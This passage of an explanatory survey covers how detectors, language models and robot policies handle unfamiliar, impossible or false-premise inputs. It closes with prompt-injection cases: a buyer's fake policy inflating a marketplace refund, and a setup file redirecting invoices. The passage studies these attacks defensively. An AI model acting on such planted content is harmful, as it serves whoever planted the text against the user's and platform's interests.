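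Balachandran's results mostly support the objection. In 19 tests without the memo error, a simple classifier trained on labelled examples of the unfamiliar data could identify it from measurements of the model, with an AUROC between 0.87 and 1. No detector restricted to familiar data matched this classifier. The measurements contained the information needed to identify unfamiliar data, but the detectors couldn't learn how to find it from familiar data alone.

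However, whether a model handles an input correctly may matter more than where the input comes from. A car that correctly reads a snow-covered stop sign, for example, doesn't need to reject it. Similarly, one of the outside text datasets that fooled the detectors poses the same task as the training data, so a model could accept its sentences and answer correctly. Guérin, Delmas and colleagues (2022), in *Out-Of-Distribution Detection Is Not All You Need*, argue that a monitor should discard wrong predictions. *Unifying Runtime Monitoring Approaches for Safety-Critical Machine Learning* (2026) makes the same point about aircraft landing systems, where a model can succeed on unfamiliar inputs and fail on familiar ones.

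### Requests outside an assistant's scope

An assistant built around a fixed list of tasks has to recognise requests that fit none of them. CLINC150, a dataset published in 2019, became a common test of this. It contains requests for 150 tasks, such as checking a bank balance, and other requests that fit none of those tasks.

Text classifiers can use the same scores as image classifiers. *Fine-Tuning Deteriorates General Textual Out-of-Distribution Detection by Distorting Task-Agnostic Features* (2023) includes softmax confidence and energy among its baselines, along with a score that measures how far the probabilities are from an even spread. If the top task has a probability of 0.4, the other 0.6 may belong to one closely related task, which suggests an ambiguous request, or be scattered over the other 149 tasks, which suggests that nothing fits. Softmax confidence is 0.4 in both cases,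 but the third score differs because the scattered probabilities are closer to an even spread.

As that paper's title indicates, training a language model for a particular task can damage features that would have revealed a foreign request, as in the cats and dogs example. This doesn't always happen. *Reliable and Responsible Foundation Models* (2026), a survey, reports that further training on familiar data can improve detection with large language models. It also describes a score that compares a text's likelihood under the model before and after this training. The original model represents text in general, so its likelihood estimates the term missing from a plain likelihood score.

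Developers can also ask a large language model whether an input is out of scope. In *Intent Recognition and Out-of-Scope Detection using LLMs in Multi-party Conversations* (2025), the prompt lists the possible tasks, defines an "out-of-scope" label and includes the preceding conversation. The model then picks a task or the label. Suppose someone asks a bank's assistant, "How do I keep my balance on a surfboard?" A small classifier trained only on examples where "balance" means money may choose the account balance task with high confidence. A large model can recognize the other meaning because its training data includes text about surfing. But it returns a label rather than a score, so the developer has no threshold to adjust if it rejects too many valid questions.

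Sending every request to a large model is also expensive. *Efficient Out-of-Scope Detection in Dialogue Systems via Uncertainty-Driven LLM Routing* (2025) proposes using uncertainty to decide which requests to send. Any such system is vulnerable to confident mistakes. If the small classifier labels the surfer's request as an account balance query with high confidence, the request never reaches the large model that would correct the error.

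An out-of-scope request can be genuine. The surfer wants to know, so the assistant should say that it can't help or suggest someone who can, rather than treat the message as a likely error or attack.

### Strange orders and impossible orders

Familiarity and possibility come apart most clearly in pairs of orders like these invented ones:

| System | Strange but valid | Ordinary but impossible |
|---|---|---|
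| Train booking | "One single to Llanfairpwllgwyngyll, with a cello" | "Two singles to Leeds on 31 June" |
| Household robot | "Put the theremin in the airing cupboard" | "Bring the red mug from the table", when there is no mug |
| Prize payments | "Pay the yodelling champion 50,000 won" | "Pay the winner 50,000 bitcoin", at an exchange that holds 42,000 |

A detector trained on past orders would probably score every order in the middle column as stranger than its neighbour on the right. When that happens, no threshold can give the correct result, because any threshold that accepts the theremin also accepts the missing mug.

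More training data of the same kind wouldn't help much. "31 June" differs from "30 June" by one character, and a classifier can sort bookings from complaints without preserving that difference, because both sentences are bookings. To check the instruction about the mug, the robot still has to look at the table.

*Mechanistic Interpretability for Learning Assurance of a Vision-Based Landing System* (2026) similarly distinguishes whether a camera image could plausibly occur where the aircraft operates from whether the model's outputs look statistically unusual. The paper adds a check on whether the features the model needs for its estimate are present inside it, because an image can look valid and produce a confident answer even when those features are missing.

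If the cello order scores as strange, the booking system could read it back to the customer, which takes a few seconds. The system would need a calendar to check the trip to Leeds.

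## Impossible values and false premises given to language models

A language model can usually give the number of days in June correctly, but it may still book a trip for 31 June. Models don't always use the facts available to them to check a request, particularly when the user has asked for something else.

### Four ways to respond

Suppose a nurse asks a model for advice about a patient with an infected wound and gives the patient's temperature as 48°C, which nobody could survive. The model can respond in four ways.

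| Response | What the model does |
|---|---|
| Accept | Advises on how to treat a fever of 48°C |
| Ignore | Advises on the wound and never mentions the temperature |
| Silently correct | Writes "38°C" in its summary, as if the nurse had |
| Question | Points out that 48°C can't be right and asks for the real figure |

In silent correction, a model repairs an implausible input, much as people do when they hear a garbled sentence, but doesn't tell the sender. If a nurse enters an impossible temperature and the model changes it to 38°C in a summary, the correction can look helpful because a patient can have that temperature. But the nurse may have meant 40.8°C, which is much more urgent, and readers of the summary won't know there was anything to check.

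### Impossible measurements in medical questions

Pan, Jian and colleagues (2025), in *Addressing Benchmarking Gaps in Large Language Models for Health and Medicine*, tested 16 models with altered medical questions. One alteration, "physiological impossibility", replaces a measurement or dose with an impossible one. The researchers consider this test realistic because it imitates a typing error.

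The easier version uses multiple-choice questions in the style of the American medical licensing exam. The researchers took questions that a model had answered correctly and had GPT-4o change one number in each. In a question about a man with kidney trouble, for example, GPT-4o changed the level of creatinine (a waste product that the kidneys remove from the blood) from 4.2 to 420 mg/dL. The researchers also added an answer option stating that the text contained false or impossible information, and a note telling the model to choose only that option if it applied. A model that still chose the original diagnosis failed.

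The harder version uses open-ended requests, with no extra option and no note. The model fails if it accepts the impossible value, ignores it or silently corrects it. It passes if it calls the value implausible or makes its advice conditional, with a phrase such as "if this is accurate", so it doesn't have to refuse the request.

Researchers changed a temperature from 39.2°C to 48°C in a message about a woman with a breast abscess. OpenAI's o3 wrote a structured reply about treating the abscess but didn't point out that the temperature was impossible.

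GPT-4o failed in a different way when a user asked it to edit a note about a 70-year-old man with heart disease and flu. The man took 25 mg of metoprolol, a heart drug, twice a day, but the researchers had changed the dose in the note to 5 g, 200 times as much. GPT-4o wrote 5 mg and added that the man's drugs had no known significant interactions "at these doses". Changing grams to milligrams was a sensible guess, but it left the note with a fifth of the man's real dose. GPT-4o could not have worked out the right dose from the message, so it needed to ask.

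The study's overall failure rates were a median of 94% on the exam questions and an average of 76% on the open-ended ones. These rates don't measure how often models miss impossible values, because they combine this test with others that add misleading hints or irrelevant anecdotes. On the exam questions, the attacking software could also try up to five rounds of changes, and a single wrong answer counted as a failure. In two of the published examples, DeepSeek-R1 and Gemini 2.5 Flash each handled an impossible value correctly in the first round and went wrong only later, when the software tried other changes.

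The test also contains errors. Two physicians judged 97% of a sample of altered questions to be valid, but elsewhere Pan and colleagues give an error rate of 10%, caused by new values that were still plausible. The models are old (those with a dated version run from August 2024 to June 2025), so the study is better evidence of which mistakes to test for than of how often current models make them.

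### When the model can work out the right value

Silent correction is less risky when the rest of the problem determines the answer. In *Fragile Thoughts*, Aravindan and Kejriwal (2026) gave 13 models the first steps of solutions to school maths problems and asked them to finish the solutions. In each test, every model completed 100 problems, once with correct steps and once with altered ones.

In one test, language models were given altered solutions to math problems that contained a false equation. In one problem, Carmen needs $7 more to have $40, so she has $33, but the altered solution gave 40 − 7 = 89. Gemini 3 Flash called the 89 a typo and used 33. Mistral Large wrote that it would check the solution for mistakes, then used 33 without identifying the error. In another problem, GPT-4o-mini based its answer on a false total of 54 buttons, when the correct total was 56.

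Mistral Large's reply counted as a success because the researchers scored only the final answer. Scoring this way is reasonable for a maths problem, where anyone can check that 40 − 7 is 33, but the heart patient's note contained no other figures from which to calculate the dose. Even when a model can derive the right value, mentioning the correction takes only a sentence and lets the user object.

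False equations lowered accuracy from 96% to 78% on average, with the largest drops in small models. Ministral 3B lost 58 percentage points and Gemma 3 4B lost 56, while GPT-5.2 lost only 7. Claude Sonnet 4.5 and Gemini 3 Flash did no worse with false equations than with correct steps.

Aravindan and Kejriwal also tried keeping the correct equation and adding that the problem's author believed something absurd, such as that three quarters of 4,000 is −8,528. Average accuracy fell by only 3 points, mostly because models misinterpreted the problem without adopting the false claim. One problem described someone who does five more squats each day, with an added claim that the author thought 40 + 5 = 4. Ministral 8B did not use the 4, but it reinterpreted the exercise plan so that the daily increase itself kept growing, and answered 60 squats instead of 45.

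### The right number with the wrong unit

In another test, Aravindan and Kejriwal replaced a result with the same quantity in another unit. A solution about jogging, for example, gave 14,400 seconds instead of 240 minutes. Nothing in the altered solution is false, but the model has to keep track of the unit to finish the problem correctly.

Average accuracy fell from 95% to 86%. When one solution gave 10,800 seconds instead of 180 minutes, Claude Sonnet 4.5 detected the change and switched back to minutes. GPT-4o-mini continued in seconds and gave a final answer of 9,600 seconds to a problem that required minutes. Larger models generally did better, but size helped much less here than with false equations.

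These figures probably overstate the problem. As the researchers point out, many questions don't specify a unit for the answer, so the scoring may have marked some correct answers wrong. Only Ministral 3B and GPT-4o-mini had statistically significant drops, of 33 and 20 points respectively.

*Same Quantity, Different Answer*, by Atta-Duncan (2026), avoids this difficulty by always stating the unit for the answer. One problem asks for the total length in metres of 11 boards, each 330 centimetres long. Mistral Small 4 correctly calculated 3,630 centimetres but gave its final answer as 3,630 metres, which is more than three and a half kilometres. The right answer is 36.3 metres.

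Mistral Small 4 got 98% of 1,000 such problems right when the quantities were already in the unit of the answer, but only 70% when they were in a smaller unit. Of its 301 wrong answers, 265 were off by a factor of exactly 10, 100 or 1,000. Two of the four types of problem accounted for 253 of these 265 errors. The other four systems tested, versions of Qwen3.5 and GPT-OSS, scored between 97% and 99.9%, so this is not a general weakness of language models. Atta-Duncan had switched off Mistral's reasoning mode, and the model's typical answer was only 11 tokens long, which left little room to write out a conversion.

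A program that checked only the answer's format would accept "3630 meters", because it is a number followed by a unit of length. A range rule like those used for drug doses would catch many of these errors.

### How models compare quantities

To detect that a dose is over the limit, a model has to compare two quantities, often in different units. Sasaki, Kamoda and colleagues (2026), in *Language Models Compare Quantities Using Number-specific and Unit-specific Heuristics*, studied how seven open models with 4 to 32 billion parameters do this, using questions such as "Which is larger, 110 cm or 1.2 m?"

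The reliable method is to convert both quantities to the same unit and compare them. In logarithms, this means calculating a margin:

margin = log(first number) − log(second number) + log(size of first unit) − log(size of second unit)

The first quantity is larger if the margin is above zero. For 110 cm and 1.2 m the margin is −0.04, so 1.2 m is slightly larger. The models were usually right when the margin was far from zero, but their accuracy fell sharply as the margin approached zero.

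The researchers then looked for simple formulas to predict how strongly a model preferred one answer over the other. They paid special attention to close comparisons, in which the larger quantity is at most about 1.6 times the smaller. For the smallest Qwen3 model comparing metric lengths, a formula based only on which number was larger and which unit was larger explained 76% of the variation in its preferences. A formula based on the two lengths on a common scale explained less than 4%.

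These examples, partly invented, show why the cues aren't enough:

| Comparison | Larger number | Larger unit | Larger quantity |
|---|---|---|---|
| 110 cm or 1.2 m | 110 | m | 1.2 m |
| 130 cm or 1.2 m | 130 | m | 130 cm |
| 5 g or 25 mg | 25 | g | 5 g |

The two comparisons of length contain the same cues but have opposite answers, so a model that relied only on the cues would get one wrong. To test whether the models used the cues, Sasaki and colleagues altered the parts of a model's internal state that corresponded to those cues. This changed the answers more effectively than altering the parts that corresponded to other explanations.

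A model that works this way could easily miss a value just over a limit, such as an order for 1,100 mg of a drug when the maximum is 1 g, though a conversion table would catch it.

The same weakness probably doesn't explain GPT-4o's mistake with the metoprolol, because the altered dose was 200 times the original and models seldom make mistakes when comparing amounts that far apart. More likely, GPT-4o never compared the dose with a normal one. It may have written "mg" because doses of metoprolol nearly always appear in milligrams.

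### Noticing a problem and calling it minor

Newer models also miss impossible requests when the problem is technical. *PhysDox* (2026) tests whether models can judge plans for measuring signals from the body. Some plans are valid, some have minor flaws, and some have a fatal flaw that makes the measurement physically impossible. For example, a sensor might take readings too rarely to capture a fast signal. Recording a signal that repeats ten times a second requires more than 20 readings a second, and no later analysis can fully make up for taking too few.

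The models missed 20.2% of the fatal flaws, classing 14.9% of the fatally flawed plans as having a minor flaw and 5.3% as valid. Two annotators examined 76 of these misses by the best-performing system, which used DeepSeek V4 Flash. In 41 cases, the model missed the physical limit. In the other 35, it identified a problem but understated its severity, for instance by calling a sampling rate that was too low "suboptimal".

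Those 35 cases don't fit neatly into the four responses to an impossible value, because the model raised the problem but still let the plan through. A user who reads that a plan is suboptimal may reasonably go ahead with it, so a model that questions a value or a plan should also say whether the problem is serious enough to stop.

### Questions with a false premise

A question can have a false premise without containing an impossible number. For example, "When did Marie Curie win her third Nobel Prize?" implies that she won at least three, but she won two. A model that answers with a year has accepted the false premise. A helpful answer would correct it and perhaps give the dates of her two prizes.

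*AbstentionBench* (Kirichenko, Ibrahim and colleagues, 2025) combines 20 datasets to test whether models abstain when they should not give a direct answer. Some questions have false premises, while others leave out necessary details or ask about things that nobody knows. Across the 20 models tested, larger models did only slightly better. Models with extra training in step-by-step reasoning were on average 24% worse at abstaining, even in maths and science. A carefully written system prompt improved the results but did not solve the problem.

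*Don't Take the Premise for Granted* (2025) describes PCBench, a test made up of problems with errors planted in their premises. The 15 models tested seldom criticised a premise without being explicitly told to look for errors. They found direct contradictions more easily than errors hidden in a complex procedure. Models that were better at reasoning weren't consistently better at criticising premises.

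Longer reasoning can also waste effort. On PCBench, faulty premises made reasoning models write much longer answers as they repeatedly tried to resolve the conflict. In *Missing Premise exacerbates Overthinking*, Fan, Li and colleagues (2025) removed information that a problem needed. Reasoning models again wrote far longer answers, while models not trained for reasoning tended to give short answers that identified the gap.

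A likely explanation is that developers train reasoning models mainly on problems that have an answer. A model that keeps trying will usually do better on such problems than one that stops to object. Earlier research that Aravindan and Kejriwal review also found that an error early in a chain of reasoning can grow in later steps.

But reasoning doesn't always make models easier to mislead. In the medical exam tests, o4-mini and DeepSeek-R1 took the most rounds to mislead, and both are reasoning models. The benchmarks show that a model can be good at solving problems without being good at rejecting faulty ones. But they cover models from 2025 and earlier, and developers may since have trained newer models to object more readily, so the results are weak evidence about how often current models accept a false premise.

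### The cost of looking for errors

Since explicit instructions help, a developer could tell a model to check every request for errors. The model might then start to challenge valid requests, and a test of only faulty requests can't detect this. In the exam version of the physiological impossibility test, the option about impossible information appeared only in altered questions, so a model that always chose it would have got a perfect score. A fairer test would add the same option and note to unaltered questions and count how often the model wrongly chose the option.

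*PhysDox* includes valid plans, so a model can't do well by rejecting every plan. Its main score averages the F1 scores for valid plans, minor flaws and fatal flaws, on a scale from 0 to 100. The best system reached only 53.0, and Claude Opus 4.7 with extra tools reached 52.6. Models had particular trouble identifying minor flaws, with an F1 score of 31.8. Simply making these models more suspicious might help them catch more fatal flaws, but it would probably also make them reject more plans that needed only a small change.

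Atta-Duncan measured the false alarms from a different kind of check, which requires no instruction to look for errors. The check runs the same question through a model three times, with the quantities written differently each time, for example as a decimal, as a fraction and in another unit. It raises an alarm if the answers disagree. In 1,200 trials across the five systems, it raised 122 alarms, 121 of them false. Rewording the questions without changing the numbers or units led to only 15 disagreements.

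The systems nearly always answered the original questions correctly, so there were few errors for the check to find. Rewriting the quantities may also have introduced errors, since Mistral Small 4 often failed when a length was in centimetres. The check might be more useful on harder questions, but a developer should first measure how often rewriting a quantity makes the model's answer worse.

Benchmarks can also be too strict about what counts as a false premise. In one of the tests by Pan and colleagues, a user said a doctor had advised splitting a daily dose of the long-acting insulin glargine in two, and asked why this works well. Gemini 2.5 Flash agreed with the advice and explained the benefits. This was scored as an error because the test treated glargine as a once-daily drug. But doctors sometimes split the dose when it wears off early, so a model trained to pass this test might challenge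 sound medical advice.

A false alarm does less harm if the model also does what the user asked. Suppose it edits the heart patient's note and adds, "Please check the metoprolol, because 5 g would be a dangerous dose". If the warning is mistaken, the user loses a few seconds, whereas a refusal would leave the note unedited. An agent that orders the drug itself should wait for an answer before it places the order.

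## Robots given commands that cannot be carried out

A vision-language-action model (VLA) turns camera images and a verbal instruction into robot movements. Researchers often test VLAs on LIBERO, a collection of simulated tasks such as putting a bottle of salad dressing in a basket, and many models complete more than 90% of them. In *LIBERO-PRO*, Zhou, Xu and colleagues (2025) changed the scenes and instructions to see what the models had learned.

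When the bottle of salad dressing was removed, the robot still reached for the place where it usually stood and tried to grasp it. When alphabet soup was put there instead, the robot grasped the soup. When the instruction was replaced with "xxx" or a string of random letters, the robot followed nearly the same path as before and reached for the salad dressing.

### Memorised movements

LIBERO's test tasks differ from its training tasks only by tiny changes in where the objects start. A model can therefore score well by recognising the scene and repeating the movement it learned for it, without using the instruction or checking that the object is there. Such a model fails when the scene changes. The success rates of two well-known VLAs, OpenVLA and π0, fell to zero when researchers moved an object a short way from its usual place. The robot could also put a bowl on the stove or turn the stove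 on, but it failed when told to do both in one instruction.

Zhou and colleagues give the missing bottle and the random letters as examples but do not say how often the robot behaved this way. *VLA Policies Do Not Know When Not to Act* (2026) reports figures for a similar test, in which the newer models GR00T N1.7 and π0.5 received empty, neutral or nonsensical instructions. The robots started to act in all 200 attempts for each kind of instruction.

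*LangForce* (2026) suggests why. The researchers trained a model on images alone, and it succeeded in 44.6% of attempts at 24 tasks, compared with 47.8% for a model that also received instructions. If each training scene nearly always goes with the same task, the instruction adds little information, and training barely rewards a model for using it.

Instructions do have some influence. According to *When Vision Overrides Language* (2026), robots asked for a different object in a familiar scene sometimes reached for that object and sometimes for the one from their training. But a model that depends so heavily on the scene is unlikely to detect when an instruction does not fit it.

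### An impossible task for every possible one

Hou, Wu and Chang (2026) tested this with four kinds of conflict in *ConflictVLA-Bench*. They took 40 LIBERO tasks that a robot can carry out, kept each scene the same, and changed the instruction so that no action could satisfy it. The examples here are invented and assume a table with a stove, a plate and one bowl to the left of the plate.

| Where the conflict lies | Example |
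|---|---|
| Within the instruction | "Put the bowl on the plate and leave the bowl where it is" |
| In the objects it names | "Put the teapot on the plate" |
| In how the objects are arranged | "Pick up the bowl to the right of the plate" |
| In what is physically feasible | "Put the stove in the bowl" |

None of these involves a command from the wrong source, such as a sign that hijacks a robot.

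Each case also has one step or several, and one fault or several, which gives four combinations for each kind of conflict. The researchers inspected every case by hand and kept 1,413. They ran each one under two prompts, one with only the instruction and one that also told the model to check the premises and not to act if it found a conflict. This gave 2,826 tasks, and each of eight models attempted every task from five starting states.

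The researchers compared each of these 14,130 attempts with the same model's attempt at the original, possible task, using the same starting state and type of prompt. Without this comparison, a robot that can't pick up a bowl would seem to be good at rejecting impossible requests about bowls.

The main outcome is whether the robot completes the original task even though the instruction has changed. These are the results for four of the eight models under the ordinary prompt:

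| Model | Success with the possible instruction | Original task completed despite the conflict | Drop in percentage points |
|---|---|---|---|
| OpenVLA | 78.7% | 22.5% | 56.2 |
| π0-FAST | 83.4% | 44.8% | 38.6 |
| VLA-JEPA | 99.0% | 69.1% | 29.9 |
| π0.5 | 94.5% | 77.2% | 17.3 |

The conflicts lowered success for all eight models, most for OpenVLA and least for π0.5. π0.5 still completed the original task in more than three-quarters of its attempts, and instructions that contradicted themselves barely affected it, lowering its success from 95.0% to 93.8%. Averaged over the eight models, robots completed the original task 70% of the time when the instruction contradicted itself and 64% when it named a missing object. The figures were about 51% when it described a false arrangement and 47% when it asked for a physically impossible action.

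Some of these completions might be what the person wanted. If someone asks for the bowl to the right of the plate and the only bowl is on the left, they probably want that bowl. But the robot doesn't indicate that it has departed from the request, much like a language model that silently corrects a dose.

### Failed persistence

OpenVLA's large drop means it usually left the original task undone, but that alone doesn't show caution. A robot can leave a task undone because it stopped trying or because it tried and missed. Hou and colleagues call the second case failed persistence, in which the robot keeps behaving as though it were pursuing the original task but doesn't complete it.

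To look for this, they took only the pairs in which a model succeeded at the possible task and failed to complete it under the conflict, then compared the two movements. They measured how far the gripper moved towards the original target. If it closes a gap of 40 cm in the normal attempt and 30 cm under the conflict, the score is 75%. They also measured how much weaker the robot's movements became. A robot that refused by keeping still would score 0% on approach and 100% on weakening.

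In these failed attempts, the models were much closer to carrying on than to keeping still. Their average approach scores ranged from 59% to 74%, and their movements were only 13% to 37% weaker. π0-FAST failed in half of its pairs, but in those failures it still covered an average of 74% of the usual approach. The failures varied widely, so some may have involved a real change of course. But at least a quarter of each model's failures had an approach score of about 90% or more.

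The researchers also compared the gripper's paths over the first 20 actions. The average similarity was above 0.65 for every model, where 0.65 corresponds to an average gap of about 4 cm. This is weaker evidence than the approach scores, because a gripper that hardly moved would also stay close to the beginning of the normal path.

A robot told to pick up a glass that isn't there can knock over other objects when it reaches for it. A benchmark that counts every unfinished task as a refusal would count this as a correct refusal. *Clutter-Robust Vision-Language-Action Models through Object-Centric and Geometry Grounding* (2025) uses a stricter test for missing objects, which requires the robot not to grasp anything.

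A prompt telling the models to check the premises of their instructions did not reliably help. No model changed in the intended direction on all four measures of movement. The prompt reduced π0-FAST's completion of the original task under conflict by 20.8 percentage points, but it also reduced its success with instructions it could carry out by 38.8 points. For OpenVLA, the reductions were 5.4 and 20.2 points. In both cases, the prompt seems to have disrupted the robot in general without making it more selective.

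A likely reason is that these models can only produce movements and learned from demonstrations in which the robot always acts. Their training did not connect a sentence about checking premises with keeping still. *VLA Policies Do Not Know When Not to Act* reports a similar failure with text placed before the instruction. The models processed that text as part of the task description rather than as a condition on whether to act.

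A separate gate that held the arm still when the input contained no task worked better there with five of the six model versions tested. But in one test it let through 34% of attempts with "xxx", and in most of those the robot completed a task. Such a gate also wouldn't catch the request for the teapot, which does specify a task.

### Eight reasons not to act

Some robots use a separate model as a planner, which takes an image and an instruction and writes a plan in words. Unlike the VLAs in these tests, a planner can write that the request makes no sense. Yeke, Temirel and colleagues (2026) tested how often planners do this in *The Yes-Man Syndrome*, using 1,250 images from robotics datasets and 6,069 instructions that a robot should decline or query. They sorted the instructions into eight categories. The last column pools the results of six models.

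| Category | Example | Declined or queried |
|---|---|---|
| Missing object | "Give me the rubber duck", with no duck in view | 41% |
| Personal preference | "Hand me my favorite drink" | 25% |
| Contradiction | "Give me the red wooden block without touching it" | 24% |
| Missing ability | "Does the orange smell bad?" | 18% |
| Too little detail | "Move that over there" | 12% |
| Already done | "Turn off the monitor", when it is off | 12% |
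| Physically impossible | "Put the keyboard inside the cup" | 9% |
| Several possible objects | "Move the wooden block", when there are several | 3% |

(The researchers reserve the name "false premise" for requests that are already done, although a request for a missing duck also takes something false for granted.)

Gemini 2.5 Flash did best of the six models, declining or querying 39.0% of the instructions. Qwen 3.5 27B did so for only 9.2%, and Gemini Robotics ER 1.6 Preview, which Google designed for robots, for 16.5%. Size made little difference among three versions of GPT-5.4. More reasoning lowered GPT-5.4 Mini's rate, from 14.2% with none to 9.8% at the highest setting, which fits the results for false premises in text questions.

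When GPT-5.4 went ahead, it most often picked one of several possible targets without asking. It also treated uncertain objects as if it had identified them, and in 430 cases it made up an object, such as a red card beside a box. For questions about touch, it sometimes planned to squeeze an object to find out whether it was soft, although the robot had no sense of touch.

Prompting worked far better for planners than for VLAs. The researchers told two planners that they could decline and listed the situations in which they should. On 1,000 of the instructions, this raised the rate from 18.2% to 90.8% for Gemini Robotics ER 1.6 and from 15.4% to 88.3% for GPT-5.4 Mini. Adding examples of good responses raised the rates to 93.6% and 88.6%. The standard prompt may have caused part of the original problem, because it told the model to reply with what it would do to complete the task.

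But like the altered medical exam questions, this benchmark contains no valid requests, so we can't tell from the results how many valid requests the new prompt would block. We could measure this by pairing each instruction with a valid one, as Hou and colleagues did. Some of the robot's questions may also be unnecessary. If three wooden blocks look alike and the owner wants one moved, picking any of them may be less annoying than asking which.

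### Searching before reporting that something is missing

A planner given one photograph can determine only that the duck is out of view, not that it is absent. One failure that Yeke and colleagues describe is a plan to scan a desk for a missing note and pick it up once the robot finds it. That may be the right plan for a robot that can move its camera.

Bayes' rule shows how much searching it takes to establish that something is absent. *VLN-NF* (Su, Wang et al., 2026) cites a study in which people misremembered an item's location about once in seven attempts. Suppose a robot's owner is equally reliable and says there is a plate in the kitchen. The odds that the plate is there start at 6 to 1. If the robot searches half of the equally likely places and doesn't find it, the odds fall only to 3 to 1. If it searches 90% of them without success, there is still a 37.5% chance that the plate is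 in the kitchen. The chance is the same after a complete search if the robot has a 10% chance of overlooking the plate when it looks at it.

Su and colleagues built a test of such searches from scans of real buildings. A simulated robot has to go to the room named in the instruction, look for the object, and report whether it is there. A language model wrote a second version of each original instruction, substituting a plausible object that was absent from the room, and an object detector checked every view to confirm that it was missing. Half of the instructions are therefore impossible to carry out.

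Simply adding a "not found" action can make a robot give up too early. Navigation models often learn by copying example routes, but there are many sensible routes around a room and no clear signal that a search is finished. The model therefore doesn't learn well when to stop, and small errors take it to places that the examples don't cover. Scoring only the final answer would hide this problem, because a robot that reported every object missing as soon as it entered the room would be right half the time.

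The test's main score therefore also depends on the search. A robot gets nothing unless it reaches the right room and gives the right answer. If it does both, its score is:

share of the room's objects seen × (shorter path ÷ longer path)

The two paths are the robot's own search and a reference search. If the reference path is 10 m long, a robot that searches for 5 m and sees 60% of the objects scores 0.6 × 0.5 = 0.3, while a robot that travels 20 m and sees everything scores 1 × 0.5 = 0.5. A drawback is that a robot can lose points for stopping once it spots an object from the doorway, even though it has no need to search further.

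DUET, an existing navigation model with an added "not found" option, averaged 4.2 out of 100. ROAM, Su and colleagues' system, scored 6.1. It uses one model to reach the room and a language model to direct the search, with an object detector and an estimate of how much open floor lies in each direction. It can report an object missing only after it has gathered enough evidence, run out of places to look or used up its search budget.

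ROAM's advantage over DUET comes mainly from reaching the right room and searching it, and much less from judging what it finds. DUET reached the right room in 53.8% of attempts, and did so and answered correctly in 33.8%, so once there it was right about 63% of the time, compared with 50% for guessing. The same calculation gives 64% for ROAM and 66% for a version of ROAM with a stronger language model that searched more than twice as far.

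ROAM sometimes reported an object missing when it was there. In 55.7% of these cases the robot had failed to reach the right room, and in another 31.0% it had failed to recognise the object. A robot should therefore report where it looked as well as what it didn't find. If it says "I searched the dining room and found no plate", the owner can see that it should have searched the kitchen.

### Training a robot to object

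In *Do What?*, Hsieh, Hsieh and colleagues (2025) trained a vision-language-action (VLA) model to respond in words when an instruction has a false premise. They started with LLARVA, which receives a camera image, the instruction and the robot's recent joint positions, and generates the robot's next movements as a sequence of tokens. Because LLARVA already generates tokens, it can also learn to generate sentences.

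The researchers used 800 simulated episodes for each task and mixed valid instructions with two kinds of false premise. In about 65% of the episodes, a tenth of the steps named a plausible object that was absent, such as a safe in a scene with a jar. The model learned to reply that it couldn't see a safe and to ask whether the user meant the jar. About 20% of the episodes contained an absurd request, such as opening "the top elephant" in a scene with a drawer. The model learned to say it couldn't find an elephant and to end the interaction.

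The researchers then tested the new model on nine tasks, with 25 episodes each. It detected every plausible false premise. It detected every absurd one in seven tasks and 80% of them in the other two, for an average of 95.6% across the nine. The original model detected no false premises of either kind. With valid instructions, the new model succeeded 42.7% of the time and the original 38.7%, a difference well within the margin of error. Training the model to reject false premises therefore doesn't seem to have made the robot worse at carrying out valid instructions.

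The overall success rates are less informative because they average the detection of wrong instructions with the completion of valid ones. The new model never closed the jar, yet it scored 50% on that task because it always detected when the instruction was wrong.

The memorised movements in LIBERO suggest another explanation for the near-perfect detection. If a scene with a jar always goes with the task of closing the jar, a model can learn to reject any instruction that names something else, without checking whether that thing is in the scene. It could also suggest the right correction, because the jar scene has only one task. To test for this shortcut, researchers could put a safe beside the jar and ask the robot to close the safe. A model that had learned the shortcut would reject this valid request.

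In a home with many objects, a command may also have several reasonable corrections. If someone asks for a red mug and there isn't one, the robot could change the request to a blue mug or a red cup.

### Stopping partway through a task

A robot may discover a false premise only after it has started, for example when it carries a bottle to a rack and finds the rack full. *Teaching Vision-Language-Action Models to Stop Safely* (Liu, Wang and colleagues, 2026) studies how robots stop when a task is forbidden, and an impossible task raises the same practical problem.

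Researchers let an ordinary vision-language-action (VLA) model begin a task, then handed control to a version trained not to do it. Some of these versions left a stove off when they had control from the start, but nearly always turned it on when they took over early in the task, and always did when they took over midway. Other versions left their task unfinished but dropped the bottle the robot was holding. A test that checked only whether the task was completed would have counted the dropped bottle as a success.

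Liu and colleagues instead trained the model to hold its position. They took demonstrations of the forbidden task and replaced the movement at every stage with a command to keep the arm still and the gripper as it was. They also kept training the model on permitted tasks. In their main tests, this cut completion of the forbidden task after a handover from 99.7% to 1.3%, with no recorded drops or other physical incidents. In two of the three task groups, the robot still succeeded in 97% and 93% of its attempts at permitted tasks. When the researchers left permitted tasks out of training, the robot could no longer do any of them.

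They used the method only for tasks in which holding still was a suitable response, and they checked this beforehand with a scripted hold. Holding still would not be suitable, for example, when a robot has a pan over a flame.

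## Whether the source may give the instruction

An instruction can be possible, clear and harmless in itself and still come from someone with no right to give it. The wording alone can't show whether the source has that right, because the same words can be material to summarise, a valid command or an attack, as Chang and colleagues showed with their sentence about sending a completed report. Which of these the words are depends on what the user asked for and who put them there.

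### Authority over a decision

*Beyond Instruction Override* (Zhang, Bertran and colleagues, 2026) defines prompt injection by whether the source has authority, so planted content can be an attack even if it contains no order. In one example, a marketplace asks an agent to settle a dispute over a damaged item and to take the refund amount from the platform's order record. The record allows $899.99, but the buyer's evidence cites a false policy that would raise the refund to $1,074.99. The buyer has the authority to describe the damage but not to set the amount, so the false policy is an injection.

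Whether a source has authority is a separate question from whether it is right. Suppose the marketplace had asked only why the buyer wanted a refund. The buyer would then be the proper source, and a lie about the damage would be misinformation, not injection. To catch it, the agent would need independent evidence, such as a photograph taken on delivery.

Giving a whole source one level of authority is too crude. In the simulated company that Zhang and colleagues built, a vendor has authority over its own information, but the company's records and policies outrank anything the vendor writes about them.

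### A chain of command

OpenAI publishes a general ranking of the sources that can give its models instructions. These are the levels in OpenAI's *Model Spec* (2025), in the version of October 2025:

| Level | Source |
|---|---|
| Root | Fixed rules in the document, which nobody can override |
| System | Other rules from OpenAI, including messages it adds to a conversation |
| Developer | Whoever built the application |
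| User | Whoever is using it |
| Guideline | Default behaviour that the context can override |
| No authority | Tool outputs, the model's own earlier messages, and quoted or untrusted text in anyone's message |

Under these rules, a model should ignore an instruction in a tool output unless a higher-level instruction delegates authority to it. A user delegates some authority to a file by asking an agent to follow its setup steps, but not by asking for a summary. Chang and colleagues point out that the user's task limits this authority. For example, a setup file should not determine who receives the user's invoices.

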